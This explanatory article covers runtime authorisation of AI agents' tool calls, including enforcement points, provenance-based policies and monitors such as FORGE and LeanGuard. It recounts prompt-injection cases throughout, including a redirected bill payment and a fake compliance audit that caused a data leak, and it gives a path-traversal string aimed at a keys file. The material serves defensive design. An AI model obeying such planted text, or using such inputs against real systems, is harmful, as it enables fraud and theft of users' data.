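# Authorising each tool call of an AI agent: enforcement points, argument provenance and human confirmation

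## Why the decision to act is taken outside the model

An AI agent is a program in which a large language model carries out a task by choosing which software functions, called tools, to run. One tool might read a file, another search the web, and another send an e-mail or move money. A tool call is the model's request to run a named tool with specific arguments, such as a file name or an account number. Tool calls let an agent book, pay for and delete things on a person's behalf, even when the model is mistaken or has been misled. Tool-call authorisation means holding each call until software that the model does not control decides whether it may run.

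### From output to effect

A language model produces only text. When part of that text follows an agreed format, the program around the model treats it as a tool call and runs the function. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) describes this process as a cycle. At each step the model receives a context, which holds the user's request and all earlier calls with their results. It produces a reply and a set of proposed calls, *C*, which may be empty. A controller, where a check can be placed, then passes a subset *E* of those calls to the tools. The results go back into the context, and the cycle repeats until the model replies without proposing a call. In an agent with no authorisation, *E* and *C* are the same set.

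Li and colleagues illustrate the danger with a payment, and a slightly expanded version of their example raises most of the questions about authorisation. A user asks an agent to pay the bill in bill.txt. The agent calls a file-reading tool and gets back the biller's account number, an amount of $100 and a due date. It then searches the user's messages to check whether someone has already paid the bill, and proposes `send_money(recipient, amount, date)` with the three values from the file. The controller passes the call to the bank's interface and the bank moves the money, which is the first change to anything outside the agent.

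Now suppose an attacker wrote one of the messages, claiming that the biller has changed banks and giving a new account number. The model may then propose a call to the same tool, with the same amount and date but with the attacker's account as the recipient. A list of permitted tools would let this call through.

### Planted text and the confused deputy

The message in the example is a prompt injection, which is text, in material the agent reads, that steers it towards an attacker's goal. The attacker may only need to send an e-mail to plant one. In the threat model of Li and colleagues, the attacker can put any text into documents, web pages and tool results, but cannot tamper with the user's request, the model or the controller.

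The underlying problem has been known for decades. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true story" about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics about its own use in a system directory, so the operators had given it permission to write files there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. When one user named the billing file as the destination for his debugging output, the operating system let the compiler overwrite it because the compiler had permission to write in that directory.

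Hardy rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler cannot refuse file names in other directories, because users have good reasons to give them. Checking for the billing file by name would leave other sensitive files in its directory unprotected. He attributes the problem to the compiler running with authority from two sources, the user who invokes it and its own licence. It cannot specify which authority it is using for which file. He proposes capabilities, tokens that each identify a file and carry the right to write to it. A user without the right to write to the billing file would have no token for that file to give the compiler.

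The bill-paying agent is in the same position as the compiler. It uses the user's authority to pay into an account whose number came from a stranger, and the bank receives a well-formed order with valid credentials. The origin of the account number is also harder to trace than that of the compiler's file name. The compiler took the file name from a slot meant for users' file names, whereas the agent's model picks the account number out of a mass of text, and nothing in the finished call shows which part of the text it came from.

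### How far training, prompts and detectors go

One reason to check actions outside the model is that it receives the request, the bill and the messages as one stream of text and has to infer which sentences are orders and which are information. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, recommends assuming that anyone who gets text into the context controls everything the model does next, including its tool calls. This is not always true, since models ignore many injections, but it is a sensible assumption for a designer who cannot tell in advance which ones they will ignore.

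Developers also cannot solve the problem by having the model ignore every instruction it finds in outside material. Li and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to log in to a website. The site emails the user a one-time code with directions to enter it on a confirmation page, and the agent has to follow those directions to complete the login.

Developers therefore try to make attacks less likely to succeed. Some filter out suspicious text before it reaches the model, but a filter strict enough to catch a coherent attack may also discard useful content. Others train the model to prefer the user's instructions, which requires access to the model's weights and gives no guarantee about any particular call. It is easier to mark outside text as untrusted, or to repeat the user's request as the work goes on. These measures all help to some degree.

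Much of the measurement comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark that combines working tools, ordinary user tasks and attacker goals. In an attacked run, the agent works on a user's task while reading material that contains text serving one of the attacker's goals. Researchers report utility, the share of user tasks the agent completes, for both clean and attacked runs. They also report attack success rate, the share of attacked runs that achieve the attacker's goal. The two figures need to be read together, because an agent that refuses to do anything has an attack success rate of zero.

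On this benchmark, Li and colleagues measured an attack success rate of 21.2% for an agent built on Qwen3-max, before they added their own check. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, measured 14.1% for agents whose only defence was repeating the user's request. In a smaller test, they told an agent running on GPT-4.1-mini not to leak confidential data, then had it summarise a document containing an injection disguised as part of a compulsory compliance audit. In all five trials, the agent sent top-secret merger plans to the attacker.

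Five trials with a small, older model show only that a prompt can fail completely. The AgentDojo figures are stronger evidence, but they cover only particular models and a particular set of attacks. A stronger model may well do better, but an attacker can try many times. If each planted text succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of *n* succeeds is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. At a success rate of 1%, a hundred attempts give the attacker a 63% chance. At 0.1%, an even chance takes about seven hundred attempts, which is not many for someone who sends e-mail in bulk. Real attempts are not independent, which can help or hinder the attacker. A model that resists one wording probably resists close copies of it, but an attacker who finds a wording that works will use it again.

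The second step of the argument therefore holds even if injection rates are low, as long as nobody can show that they will be negligible for the next attack. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues take this view in the 2025 paper on design patterns that Willison discusses. They think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while both the agents and their defences depend on the current class of language models. They advise designers to make it impossible for untrusted text to trigger a consequential action once an agent has read it. Better models could overturn this judgement, but a low injection rate on a fixed set of attacks would not be enough to do so.

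### A check the model cannot alter

A check outside the model holds regardless of what the model has come to treat as true. The idea goes back to a study for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) considered the threat from a malicious user with legitimate access who could run any program he liked. It proposed a reference monitor, which checks every reference by a program to data, a device or another program against a list of what that user may do, instead of trying to make the programs trustworthy.

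Anderson set three requirements for the checking mechanism. It must be tamper-proof, since an attacker who could modify the check could bypass it. The system must always invoke it, and any program exempt from it becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standard. It must also be small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise no one has grounds to believe it works. GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the period, failed the second and third requirements. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but the system suspended that restriction when it worked on the user's behalf. At 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, it was also too large to verify.

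A language model that checks its own calls does badly by this standard. It is not tamper-proof, because text in its context can change its decisions, and nobody can test it completely. A short set of rules in a separate program can meet both requirements, as long as the agent has no tool that can edit them.

Palumbo and colleagues built a monitor of this kind, named FORGE, which treats the model as a black box that may attempt anything. They guarantee that a call never executes if the policy (the rules on which calls may run) denies it. This guarantee depends on two conditions. Complete mediation means that the monitor intercepts every relevant call before it has any outside effect. Faithful observation means that the facts given to the policy correctly describe which tool is called, with which arguments and under whose identity, and which earlier events may have influenced the call.

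The guarantee covers only the policy as written. In the bill example, suppose the policy allows any payment under $200. The call with the attacker's account number is for $100, so the monitor correctly applies the policy and lets the payment through. Palumbo and colleagues acknowledge that a policy that permits an unsafe action will also permit it at run time, and that if a language model translates written rules into formal ones, the translation carries no guarantee. Even a sound policy can give the wrong result if the tracking data is wrong. Suppose the policy requires the recipient to come from bill.txt, but the tracking software has wrongly recorded the attacker's account number as part of that file. The monitor would then accept the attacker's account as a valid recipient.

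The outside check can therefore still make errors, but they lie in rules and records that people can read and correct, rather than in the model's weights. The drawback is that an attacker who finds a gap in a fixed rule can exploit it every time, while a trick on a model works only some of the time.

On AgentDojo, Palumbo and colleagues cut attack success from 14.1% to 0.9% by adding a policy based on the origin of data to a setup that already repeated the user request. If both of their conditions held, the remaining attacks went through calls that the policy allowed. Adding the policy also reduced utility, from 83.7% to 62.5% in clean runs and from 72.5% to 63.8% under attack. A stricter policy they tested for comparison was about as secure, but its clean utility was only 33.2%. The check of Li and colleagues reduced attack success for Qwen3-max from 21.2% to zero and lowered clean utility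 by 2 percentage points. The two experiments differ too much to compare directly, but together they suggest that the loss of utility depends a great deal on how finely the rules distinguish good calls from bad ones.

### From access to action

The current vocabulary for such checks comes from network engineering. *A Framework for Policy-based Admission Control* (1997), a draft from the Internet standards body IETF, defines a policy decision point, where a system makes policy decisions, and a policy enforcement point, where it puts them into effect. XACML, a standard language for access rules, uses the same two terms. According to TechTarget's *XACML (Extensible Access Control Markup Language)*, the enforcement point intercepts a user's request and passes it to the decision point, which evaluates it against the policies. NIST, the US standards institute, took both terms from XACML for its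 2020 guidance on "zero trust", the doctrine that a system should never trust a request just because it comes from inside its own network.

NIST compares this kind of access control to airport security, where passengers pass one checkpoint and everyone in the boarding area is then trusted to the level of that checkpoint. The checkpoint cannot control what happens beyond it, so NIST advises keeping the trusted area as small as possible by moving the check closer to the resource. A check at login is too early for an agent, because everything the agent does for the rest of the session is then trusted on the basis of that one check.

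The check must move outside the model, and it must also cover more than whether the agent has access. The ITU (2006), the UN agency for telecommunications, defines access control as deciding whether to allow a requested access to a resource and enforcing that decision. Darapaneni, Padmaja and Chaithra (2026), in *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, use an invented case to show why this is not enough. A manufacturer's purchasing agent is allowed to read the inventory and place orders of up to 50,000 rupees. It places forty bad orders because of an instruction on a vendor's catalogue page. Access control does not stop these orders, because the agent's identity is valid, its role covers the ordering tool, and it has clearance for all the data it reads.

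A check on actions needs facts that the older kind of check never received. Those listed by Darapaneni and colleagues include the person and task the agent is acting for, the origin of the instruction, the value of the action, whether anyone can reverse it, where any data is going, and how much the agent has already spent. Besides allowing or denying a call, their check can refer it to a person. The design is their own synthesis, and they tested its logic on twelve cases but not against attackers, so it is better evidence of what information such a check needs than of how well one performs. They concede that it relies on the agent's software to label the origin of each instruction accurately, so the condition of faithful observation applies here too.

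### Bad calls without an attacker

In the purchasing case, a rule against acting on instructions from retrieved content would have stopped the first bad order. But it would not stop an agent that exceeds its task without being prompted by planted text. For example, an agent told to pay one bill might find two more in the same folder and pay those as well.

Palumbo and colleagues report this behaviour outside their attack trials. In a multi-agent system that studies the side effects of medicines, agents with written instructions about access made 40 unauthorised requests for US Food and Drug Administration data in 15 trials. With the monitor in place, they made none. The team also ran three leading models (Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview) on simulated airline and retail customer service. The agents had the business rules in their instructions but still proposed calls that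 broke them, for instance by skipping a required verification or the customer's consent.

Here the monitor raised average task success from 74.7% to 81.5% in the airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% in retail, presumably because a denied call comes back with an explanation and the agent can try something else. The rules probably explain the contrast with the losses on AgentDojo. The airline rules describe a correct booking or refund, so a call that breaks them was likely to fail the task anyway, whereas a rule about the origin of data also catches good calls.

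A detector of planted text finds nothing in such runs, and a check on the instruction's origin passes them too, because the instruction came from the user. Stopping the two extra payments requires a limit on the calls themselves, such as allowing only one payment, to the account and for the amount given in bill.txt.

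## The enforcement point: where calls are intercepted and what it does not cover

A rule that allows one payment, to the account in bill.txt, protects the user only if every payment goes through the software that applies the rule. That software is the enforcement point, and designers can put it at four places on a call's path. Its location affects what information it can use and which calls it misses.

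In the bill example, the `send_money` call first appears in the agent's own program, where a hook (code wrapped around an existing function) can intercept it. The program may send the call through a gateway, a server that relays calls to many tools. The call then reaches the payment service, which can run its own check. At a lower level, the operating system and the network handle every file access and connection and can block some of these operations.

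| Place | Arguments | Conversation | Real effect | What never passes through it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hook in the agent's program | Yes | Yes | No, only the tool's reply | Actions by code without a hook, and by other programs |
| Gateway | Yes | Usually not | No, only the tool's reply | Tools inside the agent's program, and direct connections to a service |
| Tool service | Yes | No | Yes, within that service | Calls to every other service |
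| Operating system or network | Rarely | No | Files, processes and connections on that machine | Whatever a remote service does after accepting a permitted connection |

### From the agent's program to the network

A hook in the agent's program has the most context, because that program assembles the conversation the model receives. Palumbo and colleagues' monitor, FORGE, wraps the functions that run tools in several agent frameworks, which are libraries for building agents. It also wraps two common Python libraries for web requests, so it can intercept a tool that contacts a website on its own. Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit attaches to extension points that the frameworks already provide, according to Help Net Security's *Microsoft releases open-source toolkit to govern autonomous AI agents*.

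A hook's weakness is that it runs inside the program it restrains. In *AEGIS*, Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026) present a firewall that patches the client libraries agents use to reach their models. They state that it does not protect against calls made outside a patched client. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* classes its toolkit as application middleware rather than operating-system isolation, and recommends adding containers (isolated environments for programs) and network rules underneath. In both FORGE and AEGIS, a separate server decides whether to allow a call. FORGE also verifies the user's credentials there, so the agent's program cannot gain rights by naming a different user.

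Many gateways handle the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format in which an agent's program asks a server what tools it offers and then calls them. Microsoft points out that MCP has no built-in step for checking a call against a policy before it runs. A gateway can add that step for every agent behind it without changes to the agents. Amazon's cloud division, AWS, released such a check for general use in March 2026 (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026). Its policy engine evaluates each request that crosses the gateway, using rules that can refer to the user's identity and the call's arguments. But AWS lists no way for a rule to read the conversation, so a rule can refuse a payment over $200 but cannot by itself establish that the account number came from a stranger's message.

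The payment service has information that hooks and gateways lack, such as who owns the receiving account and whether someone has already paid the bill. Every payment also ends there, whichever route it took. Baran (2026), in *Authorizing MCP tool calls at the gateway or inside the proxy*, cites industry guidance that requires a check at every hop and again at the tool or data system. Baran writes for Cerbos, which sells policy engines, but the argument applies to any product, since "a proxy only authorizes what crosses it". The service must also receive the identity of the user the agent is acting for. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* warns that otherwise every call runs with the agent's own permissions and the service cannot apply the user's limits, which is Hardy's confused deputy problem.

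A network boundary has almost none of this information. On an encrypted connection to the bank, it has the bank's address but usually not the recipient or the amount. But it can stop a program from contacting the bank except through the gateway.

Keeping credentials away from the agent also limits what it can gain by bypassing the enforcement point. An agent that never holds the bank's credential gains little by reaching the bank another way. The AWS gateway manages the credentials for the tools behind it, and FORGE can add a credential to a web request when it releases the request. Microsoft's toolkit does not manage credentials, so an agent that received an e-mail token for one task may still hold it during the next.

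### One payment through FORGE

Suppose the agent has read bill.txt and searched the user's messages, and the model proposes `send_money` with the attacker's account number. FORGE's hook suspends the call and requests a verdict from the monitor. The monitor first identifies the message in which the model proposed the call, because the search for earlier influences starts there.

FORGE then waits until its records are up to date before giving a verdict. It keeps a graph of events, in which every message, tool call and result is linked to the earlier events that may have influenced it. Each process that evaluates the policy holds a copy of this graph and receives numbered updates. The request for a verdict includes the number of the update by which the call's whole history was in the graph, and the process does not return a verdict until its copy includes all updates up to that number.

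The wait matters because the policy language treats anything missing from the record as false. If a rule denied payments influenced by a stranger's message, but the result of the message search had not yet been recorded, an influenced payment would go through. A rule that required a supervisor's approval would have the opposite problem, blocking an approved payment because the approval had not yet been recorded.

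Next, the monitor gathers facts about the call, including its tool and arguments. It gets facts about the user and the user's roles from the verified credentials, and it gets facts about the file read and the message search from the graph. It then evaluates the policy, which is written in the logic language Datalog, against all of these facts together.

If the rules produce a denial, FORGE blocks the payment and returns an explanation, even if another rule would allow it. If they produce only a permission, the hook releases the call to the bank. If they produce neither, FORGE applies a default chosen by the deployer. For a payment tool the safer default is to deny, because a missing rule then causes a refusal instead of a transfer. AWS's gateway policy denies by default, and any prohibition overrides a permission.

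Checking each call adds little delay. In airline customer-service tests with 32 agents running at once, Palumbo and colleagues measured a median delay of 0.19 milliseconds at the server and 0.72 milliseconds from the agent's side. When they replayed recorded requests, the monitor made about 24,000 decisions a second, but the replay used a fixed graph already in memory, so that figure excludes the work of keeping the graph current. Yuan and colleagues measured a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds for AEGIS on a local installation, and they say a typical model reply takes 1 to 30 seconds.

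Refusals add more time than checks, because the agent has to call the model again. In the test with the planted compliance audit, mean time per scenario rose from 5.3 seconds without FORGE to between 7.6 and 11.1 seconds with it, depending on the policy.

### Where the guarantee stops

FORGE's guarantee has two conditions, complete mediation and faithful observation, and both depend on where the developers have placed hooks. Every channel through which a relevant action can reach the outside world needs a hook, and so does every place where a relevant event arises.

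Palumbo and colleagues note that FORGE's monitor cannot intercept a network connection that agent code opens without the wrapped libraries. The monitor may also decide on an incomplete record if a wrapped function starts several tasks in parallel and these produce messages at a point without a hook. A missing link between events in the record can make a rule about tainted data miss the attacker's message, while an extra link can only make the rule stricter. FORGE therefore links each model reply to every message in the history that the model received, whether or not the model used it.

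On AgentDojo, 0.9% of attacks still counted as successes under FORGE. Most of these were calls that FORGE had blocked but the benchmark still counted, because it treats some attempts as successes. Without them, the rate was 0.2%. The remaining successes resulted from incomplete mediation rather than from calls the policy had wrongly allowed. They involved the agent's final written answer to the user, which did not pass through the monitor in that deployment.

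### When the check fails or cannot read the call

An enforcement point also needs a rule for when no decision arrives. It can fail closed, which means refusing the call, or fail open, which means letting it run. For the bill, failing closed could delay the payment, while failing open could let through a payment that can't be recovered. Baran describes a hook that refuses the call when it cannot reach the policy engine. The guidance he cites also recommends a safe fallback, such as referring calls to a person or halting the agent, because otherwise a fault in one server stops all the agents' work.

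A system that fails closed on errors can still be configured in a way that allows calls no policy has approved. Microsoft's toolkit denies access if an error occurs while it evaluates a policy. But if a developer forgets to load any policy files, it allows every action, and its dashboard can still show the agent as "governed". Microsoft recommends a strict mode for production, in which every permitted action needs an explicit rule.

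AWS offers a trial mode with a similar risk. According to AWS's *GatewayPolicyEngineConfiguration*, a gateway in this mode records whether the policy would have allowed each call but does not enforce the decision. A team can use this mode to find mistaken refusals before they disrupt real work, but must remember to switch enforcement on.

The same caution applies to a call that the check can read only in part. AEGIS extracts text from nested arguments down to 32 levels and flags the call as suspicious if anything lies deeper. Baran notes that a gateway may read only a limited portion of a long request, so its decision covers only that portion. A missing argument can be just as misleading. If a rule requires every recipient to come from a trusted source, a payment with an empty recipient field satisfies it because there is no recipient to check. Palumbo and colleagues added a rule to their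 AgentDojo policy to deny such calls. Baran also recommends denying the call when a developer renames an argument and the rule no longer finds it, although this blocks legitimate calls until someone corrects the rule.

### Between the check and the call

Authorising a call correctly is of little use if a different call then runs. The enforcement point should therefore release the exact arguments it checked, rather than have the model or the agent's program produce them again. A person's approval has to cover those same arguments.

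Copying the arguments is not always enough. Suppose a tool took the name of a bill file instead of an account number, and read the account number from the file when it ran. Someone could change the file after the check, and the same file name would then lead to a different payment. The check would also have to preserve the contents that were checked, for example by passing the tool a copy of the file.

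Running totals can also go out of date. *Guardrails as Infrastructure* (Sigdel and Baral, 2026) describes an enforcement procedure that evaluates a call, runs it and then updates the budget. If two $100 payments arrived together under a $150 limit, both could pass before either reduced the budget. Deducting the amount at the moment of the decision, and restoring it if the payment fails, would prevent this.

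Some enforcement points change a call before releasing it. In Sigdel and Baral's procedure, the policy can require a change, such as cleaning up an argument. The enforcement point makes the change after the decision, and the altered call runs without being evaluated again. This is safe if the change can only narrow what the call does, but a change that broadens it would need a new check. The AWS arrangement in HKU SPACE AI Hub's *Secure AI agents with Policy and Lambda interceptors in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) makes the change before the decision. A function at the gateway issues a token limited to the user's own organisation, and then the policy engine evaluates the call.

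An enforcement point can also limit which tools the model sees. Baran describes a proxy that removes forbidden tools from a request before the model receives it, so the model does not, for example, plan to use a refund tool it is not allowed to call. Each call still needs to be checked, because an agent might learn the tool's name elsewhere. The AWS gateway likewise lists a tool if the policy would permit at least one possible call to it, and AWS notes that each actual call is evaluated later, with its full arguments.

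Refusing a payment call and giving a reason is better than altering the call. Lowering the amount or replacing the recipient creates a payment that neither the user nor the agent proposed, and the agent may then report the original payment as made.

### Giving a reason for a refusal

FORGE's refusals state the blocked action, the reason and often a next step. In one demonstration, a coding agent wrote a search page with a flaw that would let visitors inject database commands, then tried to publish it. FORGE refused because nobody had scanned the latest edits, and suggested running the scanner. The scanner found the flaw, the agent rewrote the query, and a later attempt to publish succeeded. The rule required a pass in the scanner's own output, so the agent could not satisfy it by claiming to have run the scan.

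In the customer-service tests, FORGE refused 93 calls across 68 of the 600 monitored airline trials, and the agent still completed the task in 52 of those 68. For the 33 combinations of task and model in which FORGE refused at least one call, Palumbo and colleagues report a success rate of 38.6% without the monitor and 69.7% with it. The rate for the other 117 combinations was 84.8% either way, so the improvement came where FORGE had intervened. No agents were given refusals without explanations, so the results do not show how much of the gain came from the explanations.

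Sigdel and Baral found a much larger drop in task success. They replayed recorded sequences of calls on simulated tools, with deliberate faults and unsafe actions mixed in. Their strictest policy blocked 68% of the unsafe actions, but task success fell from 36% with no policy to 7%. When their system refuses a call, it returns advice on how to fix it. A language model can respond by trying something else, but a replayed script can presumably do little with the advice. Their result is therefore better evidence of how strict rules affect fixed scripts than of how they affect agents.

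The reason for a refusal also has to be specific. A refusal from the AWS gateway, reproduced in Classmethod's *Confirm policy determination results in LOG_ONLY mode of Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Policy*, gives "no determining policies" as the reason. An administrator can infer that no rule permitted the call, but an agent can't tell from this which account or amount would have been acceptable.

### Shells and code execution

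All these designs work best when a call has one effect and its arguments describe that effect. A shell tool doesn't guarantee either, because it runs whatever command the model writes. Its only argument is a line of text, which can start a program that reads the bill, e-mails it to someone and contacts the bank. If the command runs a script, the effects depend on the script's contents, which may not appear in the call.

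The rule in the coding demonstration detected attempts to publish by looking for "git push" in the command. Sigdel and Baral's sample shell policy refuses commands that match a few destructive patterns. In AEGIS, Yuan and colleagues check arguments against 22 patterns, some of them for shell commands. AEGIS blocked all 48 attacks in a set they had assembled themselves, but it also flagged 6 of 500 harmless calls, all of them ordinary database queries with "or" conditions. They acknowledge that it may miss new variants. Because a program can achieve the same effect in many ways, such patterns are useful against accidents and familiar attacks but are weak protection against a determined attacker.

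Hooks in the agent's own libraries do not solve the problem either, because a command usually starts a separate program that they do not cover. Microsoft's advice to put containers and network rules beneath its toolkit is therefore especially important for shells. A developer can run the shell in a container that holds no bank credentials and can connect only to the gateway. A script then has unrestricted access to the files inside, but to make a payment it must send the gateway a separate `send_money` call, whose recipient and amount the policy can check.

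Publishing code is harder to control at the network boundary, because downloading from a code repository and publishing to it may use the same connection. If the container holds a read-only credential, the repository will refuse any attempt to publish from the shell. The developer can then offer publishing as a separate tool behind the enforcement point, with the repository and branch as named arguments. The agent can still damage files inside the container, so the developer should give it a copy of the project instead of the original.

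## The decision point: what it is asked and the rules it applies

While the enforcement point holds a call, the decision point works out whether it may run. The answer can depend on five things: the principal (the person or program the agent is acting for), the tool, the arguments, the current state of the systems involved, and the history of what the agent has read and done. As a function, this is:

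*D*(principal, tool, arguments, state, history) → allow, deny or ask

In the bill example, the principal is the user, the tool is `send_money`, and the arguments are an account number, $100 and a date. The state includes the user's balance and whether the bank has already received a payment for this bill. The history includes the file the agent read and the messages it searched. "Ask" means the enforcement point keeps holding the call until a person answers.

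*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) describes a decision point written in Lean, a programming language in which developers can also prove theorems about their programs. LeanGuard's function is deterministic, meaning the same inputs always give the same answer, so an auditor can repeat an old decision. The team replayed the records of their test runs and reproduced all 7,720 original decisions.

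LeanGuard and FORGE return only "allow" or "deny". If a customer has not yet confirmed an exchange, LeanGuard denies the call and can return a hint to ask the customer. The agent then has to propose the call again. If the decision point can also return "ask", the enforcement point can hold the call, ask the customer itself, and release the call once the customer confirms.

### Combining permissions and prohibitions

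Two rules may conflict on the same call. In both FORGE and the AWS gateway, the denial takes precedence, a convention called deny-overrides. The order of the rules therefore doesn't matter, and a new prohibition can never let more calls through. An operator can add "no payments to this account" without rereading the rest of the policy. In a system with three answers, the cautious way to extend the convention is to rank deny above ask, and ask above allow.

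Under default deny, every legitimate action needs a permission, and tasks fail when a permission they need is missing. Sankar and colleagues tested such a policy on DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents. They let agents read the customer's own records and public data but not change anything. The success rate of attacks placed directly in the agent's instructions fell from 57.9% to 5.9%, but the success rate on ordinary tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%. In telecom, where ordinary tasks rarely required changing anything, their success rate stayed at about 75%.

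LeanGuard uses three kinds of rule. A permit places a call in an authorised class, such as payments by the account holder. A requirement adds a condition that no permit can waive, and a prohibition blocks the call outright. For a call with its context *c*, and the permits *p*, requirements *r* and prohibitions *f* that apply to it:

allow(*c*) ⇔ (*p*₁ or *p*₂ or …) and (*r*₁ and *r*₂ and …) and not (*f*₁ or *f*₂ or …) and no evaluation error

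If there is no permit, the first bracket is false, so default deny follows from the formula.

The last condition covers missing information. Suppose a rule prohibits payment of bills the user has already paid, and the bank does not reply when the decision point checks a bill's status. A program that treats the missing answer as "not paid" will allow the payment. LeanGuard treats the failed lookup as an error and denies the call. FORGE's policy language, Datalog, treats missing facts as false, so a FORGE policy should require evidence that the bill is unpaid instead of prohibiting payment of paid bills.

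### A policy for the bill payment

A policy for `send_money` could combine these rules:

| Rule | Condition | A call it stops |
|---|---|---|
| Permit | The agent is acting for the account holder | A payment requested by another user |
| Type | One valid account number, one amount in dollars, one calendar date | A list of two recipients |
| Range | More than $0 and at most $200, dated within the next 30 days | A payment of $1,000 |
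| Allowlist | The recipient is one of the user's saved payees | A payment to an unknown account |
| Budget | This month's payments, including this one, total at most $300 | A payment of $100 after $250 of others |
| Single use | The task has no earlier payment, finished or pending | A second payment for the same bill |

If the user has already paid $150 this month, the $100 bill brings the total to $250 and passes. If the other rules fail, the budget still limits an attacker to the remaining $150.

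The single-use rule needs care when the bank does not confirm a payment, because the agent may retry a payment that has already gone through. LeanGuard records a reservation before the tool runs and keeps it if the outcome is unknown. The agent then cannot repeat the payment, and the amount still counts towards the budget. Someone must find out whether the payment went through before the reservation can safely be released.

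### Putting values in one standard form

Most of these rules compare values, which works only if the values are written in the same way. For example, banks print international account numbers in groups of four characters, but computers usually store them without spaces. A character-by-character comparison would treat the two versions as different accounts. An allowlist would then refuse a legitimate payee, which is inconvenient but safe, while a blocklist would let a blocked payee through.

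File paths are a common source of such mistakes. Suppose a rule lets the agent read any file whose path starts with `/home/ana/bills/`. The path `/home/ana/bills/../private/keys.txt` passes, but the two dots move up one folder, so the tool opens `/home/ana/private/keys.txt`. A symbolic link, a file that points to another location, can have the same effect without any dots. The decision point therefore has to work out which file the path leads to before checking whether that file is in the permitted folder.

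Rules for e-mail addresses must compare the whole domain. A rule that only searches for "mybank.com" would accept `billing@mybank.com.example.net`, an address that whoever controls example.net also controls. Letters from other alphabets can also make two different domains look identical. Amounts need a stated currency and number format, since "1.000" means one in the United States and one thousand in Germany.

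The safest order is to convert the value, check the converted value and pass that same value to the tool. A tool that receives the original text may interpret it differently from the decision point. If a value cannot be converted, the decision point should treat this as an error and deny the call.

### When nothing constrains the recipient

Conversion makes an account number comparable but does not show that the number belongs to the right person. Without the allowlist, the attacker's call would satisfy every rule in the table.

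The allowlist stops this payment because the attacker is not a saved payee. But it also stops the first payment to any new biller, and it would let the agent pay the user's landlord instead of the electricity company. To tie the recipient to this bill, the policy needs a rule about where the account number came from.

Palumbo and colleagues found a similar gap in their own policy for AgentDojo. In one travel task, the user wanted a highly rated hotel below a certain price, and an attacker planted an instruction to book the most expensive hotel in Paris for the same dates. That hotel was in a trusted catalogue and the dates matched the request, but no rule checked the price or rating. FORGE allowed the booking in three of 4,745 attacked runs, all in a setup that did not repeat the user's request.

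### What policy languages can express

Type, range and allowlist checks need only the call and a fixed list. JSON Schema, a standard format for describing structured data, can express them, and Progent, an access-control system for agents, uses rules of this kind. Cedar, developed by Amazon, and Rego, the language of the Open Policy Agent project, are general languages for access rules. Palumbo and colleagues say they are designed for decisions based on identity, group membership and the attributes of a resource. Either could express "the account holder may pay a saved payee up to $200". The budget rule would need other software to supply the amount already spent.

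The languages differ most when a rule has to follow a chain of events. Suppose one agent summarises the user's messages and passes the summary to a second agent, which makes the payment. The payment depends on the summary, and the summary depends on the attacker's message. A rule that looks only at what directly influenced the payment will miss the message. Datalog can follow the chain with two rules:

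```
Influenced(e) :- StrangerText(e).
Influenced(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), Influenced(d).
```

The first rule marks an event as influenced if it is text from a stranger. The second marks an event as influenced if it depends on another influenced event. Because the second rule refers to itself, it covers a chain of any length, and the rule's author doesn't have to decide in advance how many steps to check.

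Datalog is restricted enough that evaluating even recursive rules on a finite set of facts always ends. Evaluation gives one result, and the work grows polynomially with the number of facts. Rules can use "not" as long as no rule depends on its own negation. An operator can check a Datalog policy for problems such as contradictions or redundant rules before using it, but these checks are not always complete for recursive policies.

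| Rules | What they test most easily | Chains of events |
|---|---|---|
| JSON Schema (Progent) | The arguments of one call | No |
| Cedar | Identity, groups and attributes | Only if other software follows the chain first |
| Rego | Identity, groups and other structured data | With a built-in graph search, if it receives the event record |
| LeanGuard | Current state, and the order and timing of events | Its built-in operators follow order, but not influence |
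| Datalog (FORGE) | The call, identity and a graph of events | Yes, through recursion |

Palumbo and colleagues compare FORGE with six other systems for controlling agents, including Progent, on criteria they chose themselves, and find that only FORGE supports recursive rules. Recursive rules matter less if the software around the agent follows the chain and passes the result to the decision point. A Cedar rule could then deny any payment marked as influenced by a stranger. But each new question about the chain would need new code, whereas in Datalog it needs only a new rule.

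Datalog also has no built-in notion of time, so a limit such as two payments a day requires extra bookkeeping with timestamps. LeanGuard has operators that check whether a condition was true at the previous event, was true at least once before, or has stayed true since some event. A rule can restrict these checks to a time window, or to events that concern the same person, conversation or resource.

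### Who writes the rules

An operator can write one policy for everyone who uses an agent, but users may want different limits. Michael and Roesner (2026) reviewed 21 proposals for permissions that vary by user in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, and tried five commercial agents from Anthropic and OpenAI. In five of the proposals, users cannot state a policy, so a model predicts one from their request or other context. In six, users describe their policy in ordinary language. The rest use fixed choices such as "always", "once" and "never", labels on data, structured rules or program code.

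Michael and Roesner looked for three qualities: little effort for the user, a formal policy, and enforcement that does not depend on a model's judgement. They conclude that no proposal fully combines all three. This seems slightly too strong, because their own lists place FORGE under all three. But FORGE keeps user effort low by having a model translate the user's words into Datalog, and the translation is not guaranteed to be correct. The review also found that only six proposals clearly let users change or withdraw permissions later.

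None of the 21 in the review came with a proof that its enforcement software works correctly. LeanGuard, which was not in the review, partly fills this gap. Sankar and colleagues proved that LeanGuard's evaluator gives the answer that the policy's formal meaning requires for every possible history. The proof does not cover the software that collects facts from other systems or the step that turns a conversation into a record of consent.

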